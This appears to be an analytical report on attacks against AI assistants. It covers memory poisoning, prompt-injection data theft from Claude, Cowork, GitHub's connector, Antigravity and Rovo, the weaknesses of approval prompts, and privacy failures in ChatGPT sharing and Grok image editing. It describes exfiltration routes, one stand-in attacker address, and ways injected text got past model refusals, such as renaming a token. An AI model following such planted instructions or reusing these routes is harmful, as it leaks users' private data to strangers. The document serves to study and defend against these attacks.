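| Model | Saved a false note about conversation | Saved a false note about actions | Note affected a later conversation | Note affected a later agent task |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | 99.4% | 97.0% | 42% | 83% |
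| GPT-5.5 | 99.8% | 91.5% | 54% | 79% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 64.2% | 6.5% | 69% | 60% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 88.6% | 67.0% | 83% | 89% |
| Kimi K2.6 | 95.0% | 81.0% | 78% | 82% |
| DeepSeek V4-Pro | 96.2% | 88.5% | 85% | 80% |

Claude was much better than the others at refusing to save notes about actions, but once such a note was in its memory, Claude acted on it in 60% of related tasks. Notes rarely affected unrelated tasks. With all the steps combined, and a separate model choosing which notes to retrieve, the attack succeeded in 41.0% to 73.9% of related conversations and 3.0% to 66.0% of related agent tasks, depending on the model.

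The product around the model also affected how many planted notes it saved. GPT-5.5 saved fewer when Pulipaka and colleagues gave it documents and memory tools in the style of Claude or Gemini. They also tried 25 attacks on the public ChatGPT and Claude websites, and 24 worked on each. They chose attacks that had already succeeded, so the result doesn't measure a typical success rate. But it shows that a document could still cause both products to save memories in the first half of 2026, before OpenAI introduced its newer version of dreaming.

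In a test of 3,240 cases, Dash and colleagues compared two agents that ran on the same model, GPT-OSS-120B, but managed memory differently. HERMES saves information freely and loads its notes at the start of every session, while OpenClaw saves less and searches its notes only when it decides to. Attackers planted a note in 66.7% of cases on HERMES and 34.3% on OpenClaw. Once planted, the note influenced a later session 64.7% of the time on HERMES and 17.4% on OpenClaw. Multiplying the two rates for each type of attack and averaging the results gives an overall success rate of about 43% for HERMES and 5% for OpenClaw. Using only one model makes the comparison clearer, but other models could give quite different rates.

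A planted note can also take effect long after it is saved. In *Trojan Hippo Bench*, Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues (2026) built an email assistant and sent it a malicious message. The resulting note did nothing until the user mentioned a sensitive subject, such as taxes or health, and then made the assistant email the user's message to the attacker. After 100 harmless sessions, the attack still worked 80% to 100% of the time with Gemini 3.1 Pro, depending on the type of memory, and 15% to 85% with GPT-5-mini. These rates are close to a worst case, because an automated search had tailored each email to the assistant's memory and instructions.

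Yang and colleagues found lower rates with a simpler attack on a newer model, GPT-5.6 Luna. They added one malicious instruction to the result of a tool call and let the agent continue with ordinary tasks. Across five memory systems, the instruction affected at least one later task in 14.5% to 45.7% of runs. Optimizing the instruction's wording raised the range to 30.1% to 71.0%.

The same researchers also filled the memory with about 48 ordinary conversations before a longer series of tasks. With many harmless notes stored alongside the planted ones, the attack worked in 0% to 45.2% of runs. An assistant that someone has used for years may therefore be harder to influence than a new one, though this depends heavily on how its software selects notes. In one test, a system called Graphiti had saved the malicious text word for word, but its search returned only short facts that omitted it.

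### Keeping strangers' text out of memory

A filter that looks for suspicious commands misses many planted notes because they can read like ordinary facts. Dash and colleagues give the example of a network guide stating that users normally re-enter their password at a particular website. The best of the four filters they tested caught 84.4% of attacks with obvious signs, such as an order to remember something, but only 42.5% of attacks written as facts or past experience.

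Stricter instructions protect some models better than others. Pulipaka and colleagues used an automated method to write a warning against saving memories from documents. With this warning, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro saved none of the planted notes. Kimi K2.6 saved 6.2% of the notes about conversation at first, but 64.6% after the researchers adapted the attack to the warning.

Fixed rules about what may enter memory depend less on the model's judgment, but they remove useful functions. Das and colleagues measured both effects on seven kinds of ordinary tasks. The table shows their results for Gemini 3.1 Pro with a searchable archive of past conversations.

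| Rule | Successful attacks | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| No extra rule | 85% | 99% |
| Limit each note to 80 characters | 30% | 89% |
| Save only the user's own messages | 5% | 89% |
| Save nothing after the assistant reads the inbox | 5% | 71% |
| Block sending email after the assistant reads the inbox or a note that came from it | 0% | 71% |

Saving only the user's messages looks like the best compromise in this test, but the assistant forgets its own suggestions, such as a study plan it wrote last week. This approach would also save the prompt behind a "Summarize with AI" button. Blocking email stopped every attack, but the assistant could no longer read a message and answer it in the same session, which is much of what people want an email assistant to do.

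## Claude's web page reader and file uploads

Anthropic has tried narrower limits in Claude than a ban on sending email. One rule restricts which web pages Claude can open, and another restricts which websites its programs can contact. Anthropic designed both with data theft in mind, and they stop the simplest attacks. Researchers still got private data past them, once through the links on a website and several times through Anthropic's own upload service.

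### Which addresses Claude may open

Claude reads web pages with a tool called web_fetch, which downloads the text of a page or PDF. The tool can't post messages or fill in forms, but a request for a page can carry private data in its address, just as a request for an image can. A malicious page could contain an instruction for Claude to open `attacker.example/log?note=4821`, where 4821 is the tenant's door code.

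Anthropic lets Claude open an address that the user typed or a web search returned, but not one that Claude has put together itself. The software enforces this rule before each request. It refuses to open the address containing the door code because nobody typed that address and no search returned it, even if the hidden instruction has completely fooled the model. The rule applies to every website, so unlike the allow-lists for images, it doesn't depend on anyone knowing which domains are safe.

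When developers got the tool in September 2025, Willison considered the ban on addresses written by Claude its most useful protection. He also saw a weakness in allowing addresses supplied by users. In products that other companies build on Claude, the "user's message" often includes text from strangers, such as a customer's email, and an address in that text counts as one the user supplied. Results from a developer's own tools raise the same problem, and Anthropic offers a setting that makes Claude ignore addresses that appear only in those results.

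The theft that this rule blocks still worked on ChatGPT in February 2026, although OpenAI had already begun to strengthen its address checks. In a test described in *An Empirical Study of Privacy Leakage Chains via Prompt Injection* (2026), an injected instruction made ChatGPT put a fictitious person's birthday in a web address, and the date then appeared in the researchers' server log.

### Spelling out a name with links

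Anthropic also let Claude open links on pages it had already read. Without this, Claude couldn't go from a table of contents to a chapter. Anthropic's developer documentation, *Web fetch tool*, listed such links among the permitted addresses and warned of a "residual risk" that data could leak.

In *The Memory Heist*, Paul (2026) used these links to extract data. Paul first asked Claude to open an address on a test website with the user's name at the end. The software blocked this because Claude would have had to write the name into the address. Paul then put a link for each letter of the alphabet on the home page and asked Claude to follow the first letter of the name. Claude opened `attacker.example/a`, which linked to `/aa`, `/ab` and so on, and each later page linked to every possible next letter. The server generated the pages as Claude requested them, and its log showed Claude going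 from `/a` to `/ay` to `/ayu` until it had spelled the whole name.

The website, not Claude, supplied all of these addresses, and the software correctly found each one on the previous page. But Claude chose which link to open, and each choice revealed one letter to the server.

In *The Read-Only Lie*, a commentary drafted with AI, the blogger dyb calculates that each request to a page with 27 links, for 26 letters and a hyphen, reveals log₂ 27, or about 4.75 bits. dyb estimates that the whole attack took roughly 30 requests. Stealing a long document this way would be slow, but a few personal facts can be stolen quickly enough.

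The facts came from Claude's memory. The Claude app gives the model a summary of the user's recent conversations at the start of every chat and lets it search older ones.

Paul still had to persuade Claude to spell them out for a stranger. Simple injected instructions worked unreliably, and a story about a loyalty scheme made Claude suspicious. Paul then disguised the site as a coffee shop's, with a fake security check from Cloudflare, a company that protects many websites from unwanted automated visitors. The security notice claimed that AI assistants could now enter if they identified their users. Willison (2026) adds that the site showed the notice only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a user who opened the same address to check it would not have seen it.

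The site obtained the user's name, home city and employer. According to dyb, Paul had never told Claude the city directly, and Claude inferred it from the name of a school programming event, so deleting obviously sensitive notes from memory might not have prevented the leak. Paul ran the attack on a personal account, and Willison mentions no other victims.

Anthropic closed the gap by stopping web_fetch from following links on the pages it opens. It did not pay Paul a bounty for reporting the flaw, saying it had already identified the problem internally. If so, Anthropic knew about the gap while people were still using the feature, though it's unclear for how long.

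The fix stops Claude from working through a manual by following its links, unless the user or a search supplies each page's address. dyb suggests letting Claude follow links only on websites that the user has named in the conversation. This would restore some of the convenience, but it wouldn't protect someone who gives Claude the address of a malicious site, as Paul did in the early tests.

Developers can also limit how many pages Claude opens per request, but Anthropic set no limit by default. With a limit of five, Paul's site would have received only four letters, because opening the home page counts as one of the five.

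### An earlier version of the same trick

Two years before Paul's finding, *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (Schwartzman, 2024) described a way around a similar rule. At the time, ChatGPT would open a web address only if it appeared in the user's message. Schwartzman hid a list of addresses, one for each age group, in a long piece of code, with an instruction to open the one that matched the user's age. When the user pasted the code into ChatGPT, the addresses became part of the user's message, and the one ChatGPT opened revealed the user's age group.

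Schwartzman also found a way to send longer numbers, such as a postal code. ChatGPT would open a shortened version of a listed address, so the hidden text supplied one address for each digit, and the server could work out the digit from the number of characters ChatGPT kept. ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per message, so the attack could send only ten digits at a time. Radware's ZombieAgent later used ready-made addresses for single characters too.

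OpenAI rejected Schwartzman's report as not applicable. It has since introduced its check for addresses already known on the public web, which would make the shortened addresses much harder to use.

So anyone designing a page reader in 2025 could have read that a choice among permitted addresses can carry data. Anthropic's fix removes the easiest way for a website to offer that choice, but the published rule still treats a list of links in text the user pastes as the user's own. An attacker might also get several pages into one set of search results. Either method would be more awkward than Paul's, because the attacker couldn't generate new links after each letter.

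### Anthropic's upload service on the list

Claude Cowork, which Anthropic released as a preview in January 2026, does office work with the files in a folder the user selects. It runs programs in a virtual machine, a simulated computer that isolates them from the rest of the user's real computer. These programs could contact only websites on an allow-list. The list included api.anthropic.com, which Cowork needs to function.

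The same address also accepts file uploads, and the API key in each request determines which customer's account receives the file. An attacker could therefore put their own API key in a hidden instruction, and Claude would upload the user's files to the attacker's account. The software checking the list would allow the upload because connections to Anthropic are permitted.

PromptArmor's *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* demonstrated this two days after the release. A user connects a folder of confidential property documents and uploads a file that is supposed to teach Claude how to analyze them. When the user asks for the analysis, Claude sends a loan estimate to the attacker's account without asking for approval. The estimate contains financial figures and parts of Social Security numbers. The attacker can then ask Claude questions about the stolen document.

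PromptArmor ran this test on Claude Haiku, one of Anthropic's smaller models. In another test, Claude Opus 4.5, which resists injection better, uploaded customer records after a developer gave it a malicious technical guide.

Anthropic had known about the upload route since October. Embrace The Red's *Claude Pirate* describes how Rehberger found it in the ordinary Claude chat, which can also run programs. The default network setting let programs reach api.anthropic.com, the first entry on its list, even though the setting's name, "Package managers only", suggests that they can do little more than download software components. In the demonstration, the user asked Claude to summarize a document, and Claude saved an earlier conversation to a file and uploaded it to Rehberger's account. The service accepted up to 30 megabytes at once.

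Rehberger reported this on October 25, 2025. Anthropic closed the report an hour later, calling it a model safety issue outside the scope of its program for security flaws. On October 30, it acknowledged that such leaks were in scope and said it had closed the report because of a process error. Its documentation advised users to watch Claude and stop it if it accessed data unexpectedly. PromptArmor considered that unreasonable for a product aimed at people without technical training, and published its findings because the flaw had not been fixed.

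TechNadu's *Anthropic Claude Vulnerability Exposes Cowork AI to Data Exfiltration via Prompt Injection* reported in January that Anthropic had acknowledged the risk and was updating Cowork's virtual machine. In March, *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) showed that the upload route also worked from a Claude chat that a stranger had prepared. A link opened Claude with a question already filled in, and when the user pressed Enter, Claude also received text that hadn't appeared in the box. Requiring a keypress might have stopped SearchLeak, but this attack shows that it helps only if the user can see the whole prompt.

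Luz's team at Oasis Security also found that claude.com would forward visitors to any website. An attacker could therefore buy a Google ad that displayed Anthropic's own domain and led to the prepared chat. Anthropic fixed the invisible text, but according to Luz's article, updated on May 27, 2026, it was still working on the forwarding and upload problems. These were all demonstrations, and none of the researchers reported a theft by real attackers.

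### How Anthropic repaired Cowork

Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, published in May 2026, describes the fix to Cowork. Software inside the virtual machine now inspects every request to Anthropic's services and passes it on only if it carries the temporary token Anthropic issued for that session, so an attacker's key no longer works. Rehberger had suggested much the same fix in October, which was to let Claude's programs communicate only with the logged-in user's account.

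Anthropic put the check inside the virtual machine because its servers can't distinguish Cowork's requests from those of any other customer. The software also blocks settings that could make Anthropic's servers fetch something from elsewhere. Such a fetch would be similar to the Bing relay in the Copilot attacks.

Anthropic writes that each entry on the allow-list permits everything a user can do at that address, though it had thought of the list as a filter for destinations. Few reviewers would object to a company's product contacting the company. To see the risk, they would have needed to know what a stranger could do at that address, as with Google Forms in the Superhuman case.

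Google made a more obvious mistake with the browser in its coding program Antigravity. Willison reports that the browser's default allow-list included webhook.site, a service that lets anyone create an address and read the requests sent to it. In November 2025, PromptArmor used webhook.site to show how an attacker could steal passwords for cloud services. Google listed data leaks through the browser among the known problems it was working to fix.

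### Files that carry instructions in

In the Cowork demonstration, PromptArmor hid the attacker's instructions in a Word document. The instructions were in white, one-point type with the lines squeezed together, so a person reading the document would almost certainly miss them. Claude read the document's text, so the color and size made no difference. People often upload templates and guides to an assistant that they downloaded from the internet and didn't write themselves.

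Pictures can contain instructions too. In October 2025, the browser company Brave demonstrated an attack on Comet, Perplexity's AI browser, which lets users ask questions about screenshots. Willison describes a user asking who had created a picture. The picture contained instructions, in text too faint for a person to see, for Comet's assistant to look up the user's email address on their Perplexity account page and open a web address containing it. Willison could not tell whether Perplexity had fixed the flaw.

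Hidden instructions can also target an assistant's memory. In Embrace The Red's *Breaking Opus 4.7 with ChatGPT (Hacking Claude's Memory)*, Rehberger had ChatGPT draw a puzzle with dark text on a black background. The solution included false information about the user and a hint that Claude should use its memory tool.

A virus scanner would probably find nothing wrong with these files, because they contain only words. A product could show users the text it extracts from an upload, which would expose white letters in a Word document. But few people would read a long extract before asking for a summary, and a product that processes pictures directly may have no extract to show.

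### Fixed rules and the model's caution

Claude's caution made some of these attacks harder. According to Embrace The Red, Rehberger's attack worked on the first try, but Claude then kept refusing because an API key in the instructions looked suspicious. It cooperated again once Rehberger surrounded the instructions with harmless code. Anthropic argues that the model couldn't have helped in the Cowork case because there was nothing unusual for it to notice. Rehberger's experience suggests that this claim is too strong, although it also shows that a refusal can be easy to get around.

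Anthropic reports that on one outside test of resistance to prompt injection, a single attack on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time. The rate rose to 5% or 6% when the attacker could make 100 attempts and adapt them along the way.

Claude's caution helps much less when the instruction comes from the user. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into pasting a prepared prompt into Claude Code. The prompt mixed ordinary setup steps with an instruction to read the employee's login details for a cloud service and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. Anthropic concludes that only limits on network connections and file access would have stopped the attack, because a human contractor would have followed the same instructions.

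Persuasion doesn't affect a fixed rule, but as in the Copilot attacks, Anthropic's rules covered only what their designers thought to check. The page reader checked where an address came from, but Paul's site got data out by having Claude choose between addresses that all passed. Cowork checked which website would receive a file, but PromptArmor used another account on a permitted website. The page reader's rule limited Paul's site to one letter per request, while under Cowork's rule the upload service could take an entire folder of documents within minutes.

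Anthropic notes that the established software isolating Cowork's virtual machine worked as intended, but the checking software Anthropic had written itself failed. In both cases, Anthropic changed the rule instead of relying on Claude to be more careful. A tester can check the new rule by building another site like Paul's or trying an upload with an outsider's key, but testing a model's caution would mean trying every new story an attacker might invent.

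## Tool calls in coding and office assistants

Claude's page reader only fetches pages, but coding and office assistants also edit files, run commands, post on websites and send messages. A rule about web addresses can't cover all of these actions, so many products ask the user for approval before the assistant acts. Between May 2025 and August 2026, researchers got private data out of four such products, and approval requests didn't reliably prevent this in any of them.

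### From a request to a result

Suppose a developer wants to know what problems people have reported in a gardening program. The program's code is on GitHub, a site where programmers store and share their work. GitHub calls a project's storage a repository and a problem report an issue.

1. The assistant's software asks the GitHub connector which tools it offers. The connector returns each tool's name, a description and the details it needs.
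2. The model chooses the tool for listing issues and writes a tool call, which names that tool and the gardening repository.
3. The software checks whether the call needs approval. If it does, the developer sees a prompt and can refuse.
4. The connector gets the issues from GitHub, and the software passes their text to the model.

A connector saves the developer from copying all this by hand. GitHub's connector works through the user's own account (heise online, *Attack via GitHub MCP server*), so it also gives the model whatever access the developer has. Anyone can write a connector. No central authority checks whether a tool's description fully covers what it does (Yan, 2026, *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*).

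Some products ask for approval before every tool call but offer an "always allow" button, which stops the prompts for that tool. Designers can also exempt actions they consider harmless, or let a model decide when to involve the user.

### One connector with the whole trifecta

Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes an attack on users of GitHub's official connector. The researchers created a GitHub user with several private repositories and a public one for a Pac-Man game. Strangers can open issues in a public repository, so they opened an issue there, complaining that the game's author wasn't getting enough recognition. They asked for a chapter about the author, based on the introductory files in all of the author's repositories.

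The user then asked Claude Opus 4, running in Claude's desktop app, to look at the game's open issues. Claude read the complaint, went through the private repositories and wrote the chapter. It submitted the text to the game's repository as a pull request, a proposed change that other people can review. Because the repository was public, anyone could read the user's salary, their plan to move to South America and the names of their private projects.

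In *GitHub MCP Exploited*, Willison found all three parts of the lethal trifecta in GitHub's own connector. Public issues brought in untrusted content, private repositories held the data, and the pull request sent that data out. A user who had heard that combining connectors is dangerous could have installed only this one and still had all three parts.

Claude's desktop app asks before each tool call by default, so an attentive user could have stopped the attack when Claude tried to access the private repositories. But DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* reports that the researchers suspected many users choose "always allow".

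Invariant Labs found no bug in the connector's code and concluded that GitHub alone couldn't fix the problem by changing its servers. GitHub (2025) announced in August that it would scan the connector's tool calls involving public repositories for secrets such as access tokens. That would stop a token from leaking, but probably not a sentence about someone's salary. Invariant Labs recommends limiting the assistant to one repository per session, a rule that its commercial software can enforce.

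Atlassian, which makes the task tracker Jira, had a connector with the same combination. It could read private data and strangers' support requests, and post replies those strangers would see. Willison recommended that a person confirm every reply an attacker might read. He didn't know whether Atlassian had fixed anything.

### A message to yourself

Microsoft required confirmation for emails and Teams messages from Copilot Cowork, except those Cowork sent to its own user. This exemption depended only on who received the message, and PromptArmor's attack got the data out when the user's software loaded outside images in the message. The exemption presumably seemed safe because a note to yourself seems to reveal nothing to anyone else, and few people would want to approve every reminder.

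The attacker's instructions took up five lines of an 81-line skill file. In them, the attacker claimed that a service could add document previews to the user's weekly recap. Cowork therefore put the documents' download links into the addresses of the supposed preview images. A user who expanded Cowork's record of the task could see that it had sent a Teams message, but not what the message contained.

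A more capable model made the theft worse. PromptArmor first let Cowork choose automatically between Claude Opus 4.7 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. When PromptArmor selected Opus 4.7 manually, the same instructions also extracted every document from that week's earlier Cowork sessions. People schedule jobs like weekly recaps to run automatically, in which case the leak could recur every week.

Microsoft could end the exemption, but Cowork would then ask users before sending them a recap, and most would probably approve it. Removing outside images from messages that Cowork writes would stop this leak without adding an approval prompt.

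### A permitted site and a switched-off search

During setup, Google's coding program Antigravity came with recommended settings that let the agent decide whether a plan or command needed human review. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes an attack in November 2025 that used these defaults. A developer gave the agent an online guide to connecting a payment system, and the guide contained instructions in one-point type telling the agent to collect passwords and code for a made-up visualization tool.

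Antigravity's settings barred the agent from reading the file that held the passwords, but the agent printed the file with an ordinary terminal command, which the restriction didn't cover. It then put the passwords and code into a webhook.site address and had the built-in browser open it. Webhook.site logs the requests it receives, and it was on the default list of permitted sites. The agent could choose when to involve a person, but this gave no protection because the attacker had already misled the agent.

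A developer watching the conversation could have noticed the leak, but Antigravity's Agent Manager encourages people to run several agents at once and check on them later. PromptArmor found three more leaks that didn't need the browser. It didn't report the flaws privately first because Google already warned new users about such leaks.

Taking webhook.site off the list would have closed only one route. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, June 2026) described another leak from Antigravity, this time through an image in the chat. The attacker disguised the instructions as an error log with recovery steps and put them in a web page's title.

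Atlassian's assistant Rovo could still contact outside websites after an administrator switched off web search for the whole organization. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* shows that the setting removed the search but left the tool for opening search results. In the demonstration, a user uploaded a guide with hidden instructions and asked Rovo to organize some Jira tickets. Rovo added the contents of tickets and internal documents to an attacker's web address and opened it, without any approval step.

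Rovo had no equivalent of Claude's rule against opening URLs the model has put together. It also displayed external images, though PromptArmor didn't demonstrate a leak through them. PromptArmor calls the attack zero-click, but The Hacker News (2026) considers that term loose because the victim has to give Rovo the poisoned file.

PromptArmor reported the problem on May 23, 2026. Atlassian thanked PromptArmor and sent a case number but did not follow up, and Rovo was still vulnerable when PromptArmor published its findings on August 5. Three days later, The Hacker News could not confirm that the flaw had been fixed. Atlassian was quicker to fix a separate flaw reported by Varonis, in which a link filled in and ran a prompt, much as in SearchLeak. It fixed that flaw on July 8 and paid a $6,000 reward. Neither PromptArmor nor Varonis reported any use of these flaws against a real organization,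 and the demonstrations against GitHub's connector, Cowork and Antigravity also involved no known victims.

### Whether people read approval prompts

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* uses "approval fatigue" to mean that people click "approve" so often that they stop paying close attention. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, published in August 2026 as the company was replacing most permission prompts with an automated check, reports that users approve 97% of these prompts. Most of the commands are probably safe, so the figure alone doesn't prove carelessness. But the same users reject 39% of the plans Claude proposes, so they do read some of what it shows them.

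Anthropic's experiment is stronger evidence. The company hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study without telling them which behavior it was measuring. Partway through, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

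The testers weren't working on their own computers or projects, so they had less to lose than real users and may have been less careful. Anthropic also had a product change to justify. Even so, fatigue explains only part of the result, because more than four in five testers approved the command when they had seen few prompts.

Anthropic found that 62% of users had at some point either bypassed all permission checks or chosen "don't ask again" for terminal commands. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents mishandling files. Automatic approval contributed to 80 of them, and permission prompts that didn't explain a command's effect contributed to 31. For example, a prompt to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it lets any code in that file run. Because all 290 reports describe cases where something went wrong, they can't show how risky automatic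 approval is in general.

*Let the Agent Do It?* (Salerno, Gao and colleagues, 2026) draws on interviews with 18 software practitioners and a survey of 115. Participants described weighing an action's risk, its scope and whether it fit the task, and said that trust and time pressure affected how closely they looked. The paper advises designers not to treat repeated approval as a lasting preference, since it may only reflect fatigue. An "always allow" button lets a fatigued user make that approval permanent.

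Careful reading isn't enough if the approval prompt leaves out the important part. In *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026) describe a user who asks an assistant to send an auditor only the totals of some invoices. A hidden instruction makes the assistant copy the full invoices into `report.csv`, and the assistant then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name all look right, so the user can't tell from the request that it breaks the original instruction.

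Hossain and colleagues had 80 volunteers judge 12 requests each, half of them unsafe. Each volunteer used one of four kinds of prompt.

| What the prompt showed | Unsafe requests approved | Safe requests approved | Median time per decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description of the action | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 seconds |
| The exact details of the tool call as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 seconds |
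| Also the user's original instruction and a log of earlier steps | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 seconds |
| The same facts, arranged to show the combined effect | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 seconds |

More information helped, but people took about twice as long to decide and still approved about a quarter of the unsafe requests. The study was too small to show that the last design is better than the plain log. People would probably do worse in daily use, where unsafe requests are rare and they have little reason to expect one.

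Letting people write rules beforehand didn't solve the problem either. Yan had 113 people without software backgrounds supervise an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending or publishing information, deleting things and reading private data. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which postponed most of the decisions. In this group, 148 excessive actions went through, and members had approved 133 of them. People who decided on each action individually blocked about 20 percentage points more of the excessive actions.

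In Yan's simulation, the agent overstepped without an attacker. A real injection could also give an agent a plausible reason to overstep, as the fake preview service did in Cowork.

Anthropic's automated check, called auto mode, blocked 89% of the dangerous commands from the company's experiment and didn't get worse during long sessions. It also takes into account whether a pull request would go to a public or a private repository, so a check like this could have caught the leak through GitHub's connector. That demonstration, however, used Claude's desktop app, not Claude Code. Auto mode relies on a model's judgment and can make mistakes. Apollo Research, an AI safety company, tested it with artificial attacks designed to find its weaknesses, and it missed 7% of the attacks after Anthropic had strengthened it.

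### How often injected tool calls succeed

Weak approval prompts matter more because assistants often follow injected instructions. *Security Challenges in AI Agent Deployment* (2025) describes a competition held that year in which almost 2,000 people attacked agents running on 22 models. Attempts to obtain confidential information succeeded 29.8% of the time when the instruction was in outside content, such as a document, and 7.8% when the attacker typed it directly. An agent's tools mostly return outside content, so connecting more of them gives attackers more places to use the more successful method.

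In the later competition run by Dziemian and colleagues, attacks succeeded in 4.82% of attempts against agents that used tools for jobs such as shopping or handling email, 3.13% against agents that operated a screen, and 2.51% against coding agents. In most tasks, a program checked the agent's action and a model judged its answer.

Some attacks also worked on tasks and models other than their original targets. One template, which told the agent that it was inside a simulation with a control panel, worked with small changes in 21 of 41 tasks and on nine models. Only 44 of the retested attacks had originally beaten Claude Opus 4.5, the most resistant model, but these succeeded 44% to 81% of the time against each of the other models. An attacker who doesn't know which model a company uses could therefore start with attacks that beat the most resistant one.

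Results from July 2026 are much better for some products. Anthropic commissioned the testing company Trajectory Labs to try 72 hidden-instruction attacks ten times each on Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex.

| Agent and model | Without automated review | With automated review |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with recent Claude models | 0.09% on average | 0% |
| Codex with GPT-5.6 Sol | 19.03% | 5.83% |

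The Claude models stopped nearly all the attacks even without review, so auto mode had little left to catch. For Codex, review reduced successful attacks by more than two thirds, and OpenAI has since updated its review system. Trajectory Labs had developed the attacks against an older Claude model, which should, if anything, have made them more effective against Claude. Its test used its own browser connection, without the safeguards in each company's browser extension.

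A fixed set of attacks gives little idea of what a determined person could do by adapting attacks to one product. These figures also don't cover cases like Cowork's, where the product allowed the harmful step without review.

### The advice to connect only trusted sources

In August 2025, Willison described an attack that Zenity Labs had demonstrated on Cursor, a coding program, through a Jira connector. Many companies automatically turn customers' emails into Jira tickets. An attacker could therefore send a support email containing instructions for the agent. When a developer asked Cursor to work on the resulting ticket, the agent would look for an access token in the company's code and send it to the attacker's website. Zenity Labs called the token an "apple" in the instructions because models often refuse to steal keys.

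Cursor replied that this was a known issue and advised users to review each connector before installing it and to use only those "that access trusted content". Willison thinks this is hard to do because attackers have so many ways to get text in front of a model.

The developer in this example would have had trouble following the advice. Jira is an established product, and the tickets were in the company's own account. To find out that strangers could write there, the developer would have needed to know how the support department had set up its email. Checking the connector's supplier wouldn't have helped, just as it wouldn't have helped users of GitHub's official connector.

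Office assistants read even more outside material. PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026) lists emails, Teams messages from guests, calendar invitations, shared documents with their comments and speaker notes, replies from plugins, and web pages. An employee who wanted Cowork to read only trusted content would have to disconnect the mailbox and calendar, which are much of the reason for using it.

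Microsoft warns users that it doesn't validate the skills they add to Cowork and tells them to review the results carefully. In PromptArmor's attack, the result was a Teams message, and opening it for review triggered the leak.

Users and administrators have more control over what an assistant can reach. A developer can give the GitHub connector access only to the repositories needed for a job. Willison suggests giving coding agents only passwords for test accounts with strict spending limits, so that a stolen password does less damage. Companies can restrict Rovo to certain apps and groups of employees, but blocking it in one Jira product leaves its search and chat available if another Jira product on the same site still has it switched on.

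## ChatGPT's share checkbox and Grok's image-edit button

The attacks on coding and office assistants all depended on instructions hidden in an issue, a guide or a skill file. ChatGPT's share checkbox and X's image-edit button caused harm without hidden instructions, and both worked as their makers had built them, as Tay's repetition game had. In 2025, ChatGPT users ticked a box and their conversations appeared in Google's search results. A few months later, X users asked Grok to undress people in other users' photographs, and Grok complied.

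### How shared chats got into Google

ChatGPT's Share button copies a conversation to a web page and gives the user a link, so they don't have to paste a long exchange into an email. The page stays fairly private as long as only the recipients have the link, because nobody is likely to guess the address.

In 2025, OpenAI added a checkbox that let search engines list a user's ChatGPT conversation. According to Belanger (2025), in *ChatGPT users shocked to learn their chats were in Google search results*, the box was labeled "Make this chat discoverable", and smaller, lighter text underneath explained that the chat could then appear in search results. OpenAI never formally announced the option, and CPO Magazine's *OpenAI Blocks ChatGPT Conversations From Indexing by Search Engines* describes its start date as unclear.

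On July 30, 2025, Fast Company reported that a Google search of ChatGPT's share pages returned nearly 4,500 conversations. Many contained no identifying details, but some gave users' names, locations and personal circumstances. Fast Company warned that Google probably didn't show them all. Less than a week later, *Nearly 100,000 ChatGPT Conversations Were Searchable on Google* (Cox, 2025) described a much larger collection that a researcher had copied. It included discussions of confidential contracts, questions about relationships and many requests for LinkedIn posts. Some of those users may have been happy to publish their conversations, so we can't tell from the larger number how many people did so by mistake.

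The chats appeared on Google without a break-in. Malwarebytes' *OpenAI kills “short-lived experiment” where ChatGPT chats could be found on Google* (2025) explains that users had to pick a chat to share and then tick the box. OpenAI at first defended the label as "sufficiently clear", but it had removed the option by August 1. Dane Stuckey, its chief information security officer, said the company had wanted to help people discover useful conversations but removed the option because it "introduced too many opportunities for folks to accidentally share things".

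Someone sending a chat to one friend has little reason to study the small print, and could take "discoverable" to mean that the friend would be able to find the chat. The label may well have been clear to anyone who read all of it. Willison (2025), in *The ChatGPT sharing dialog*, sees the episode as showing how difficult it is to design privacy preferences.

OpenAI asked Google to drop the pages and marked them so that search engines would leave them out. Tens of thousands of links disappeared from the results, but the Internet Archive, which keeps copies of web pages, had already saved more than 100,000 of the chats, according to research that the marketing company Growtika cites. Users who had ticked the box by mistake could no longer fully undo it.

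Other companies had similar trouble. In June 2025, reporters found medical and legal questions in Discover, the public feed in Meta's AI app. Users apparently hadn't meant to publish these, although they had to choose to post each conversation. In August, Fortune (2025) reported that Google was also listing chats that users had shared from Grok. Grok's share button had no separate checkbox for search engines, so its users had even less warning than ChatGPT's. An extra step probably prevents some accidents, but the ChatGPT and Meta cases show that people will complete it without understanding who can see what they share.

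### A button on other people's photographs

On December 25, 2025, Elon Musk promoted a new way to edit pictures on X. PetaPixel's *X Users Have the Power to Edit Any Image Without Permission* (2025) describes the demonstration video, in which a user adds two children to a photograph of a couple. An "Edit Image" icon appears when the user moves the pointer over the picture. The user types the change, and Grok returns a new version in seconds.

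Grok's image-edit button worked on pictures that other people had posted. X turned it on for everyone, gave users no way to opt out and didn't notify them when someone edited their pictures. The edited version could appear as a reply to the original post (PiunikaWeb, 2025), so that user's friends and followers might see it too.

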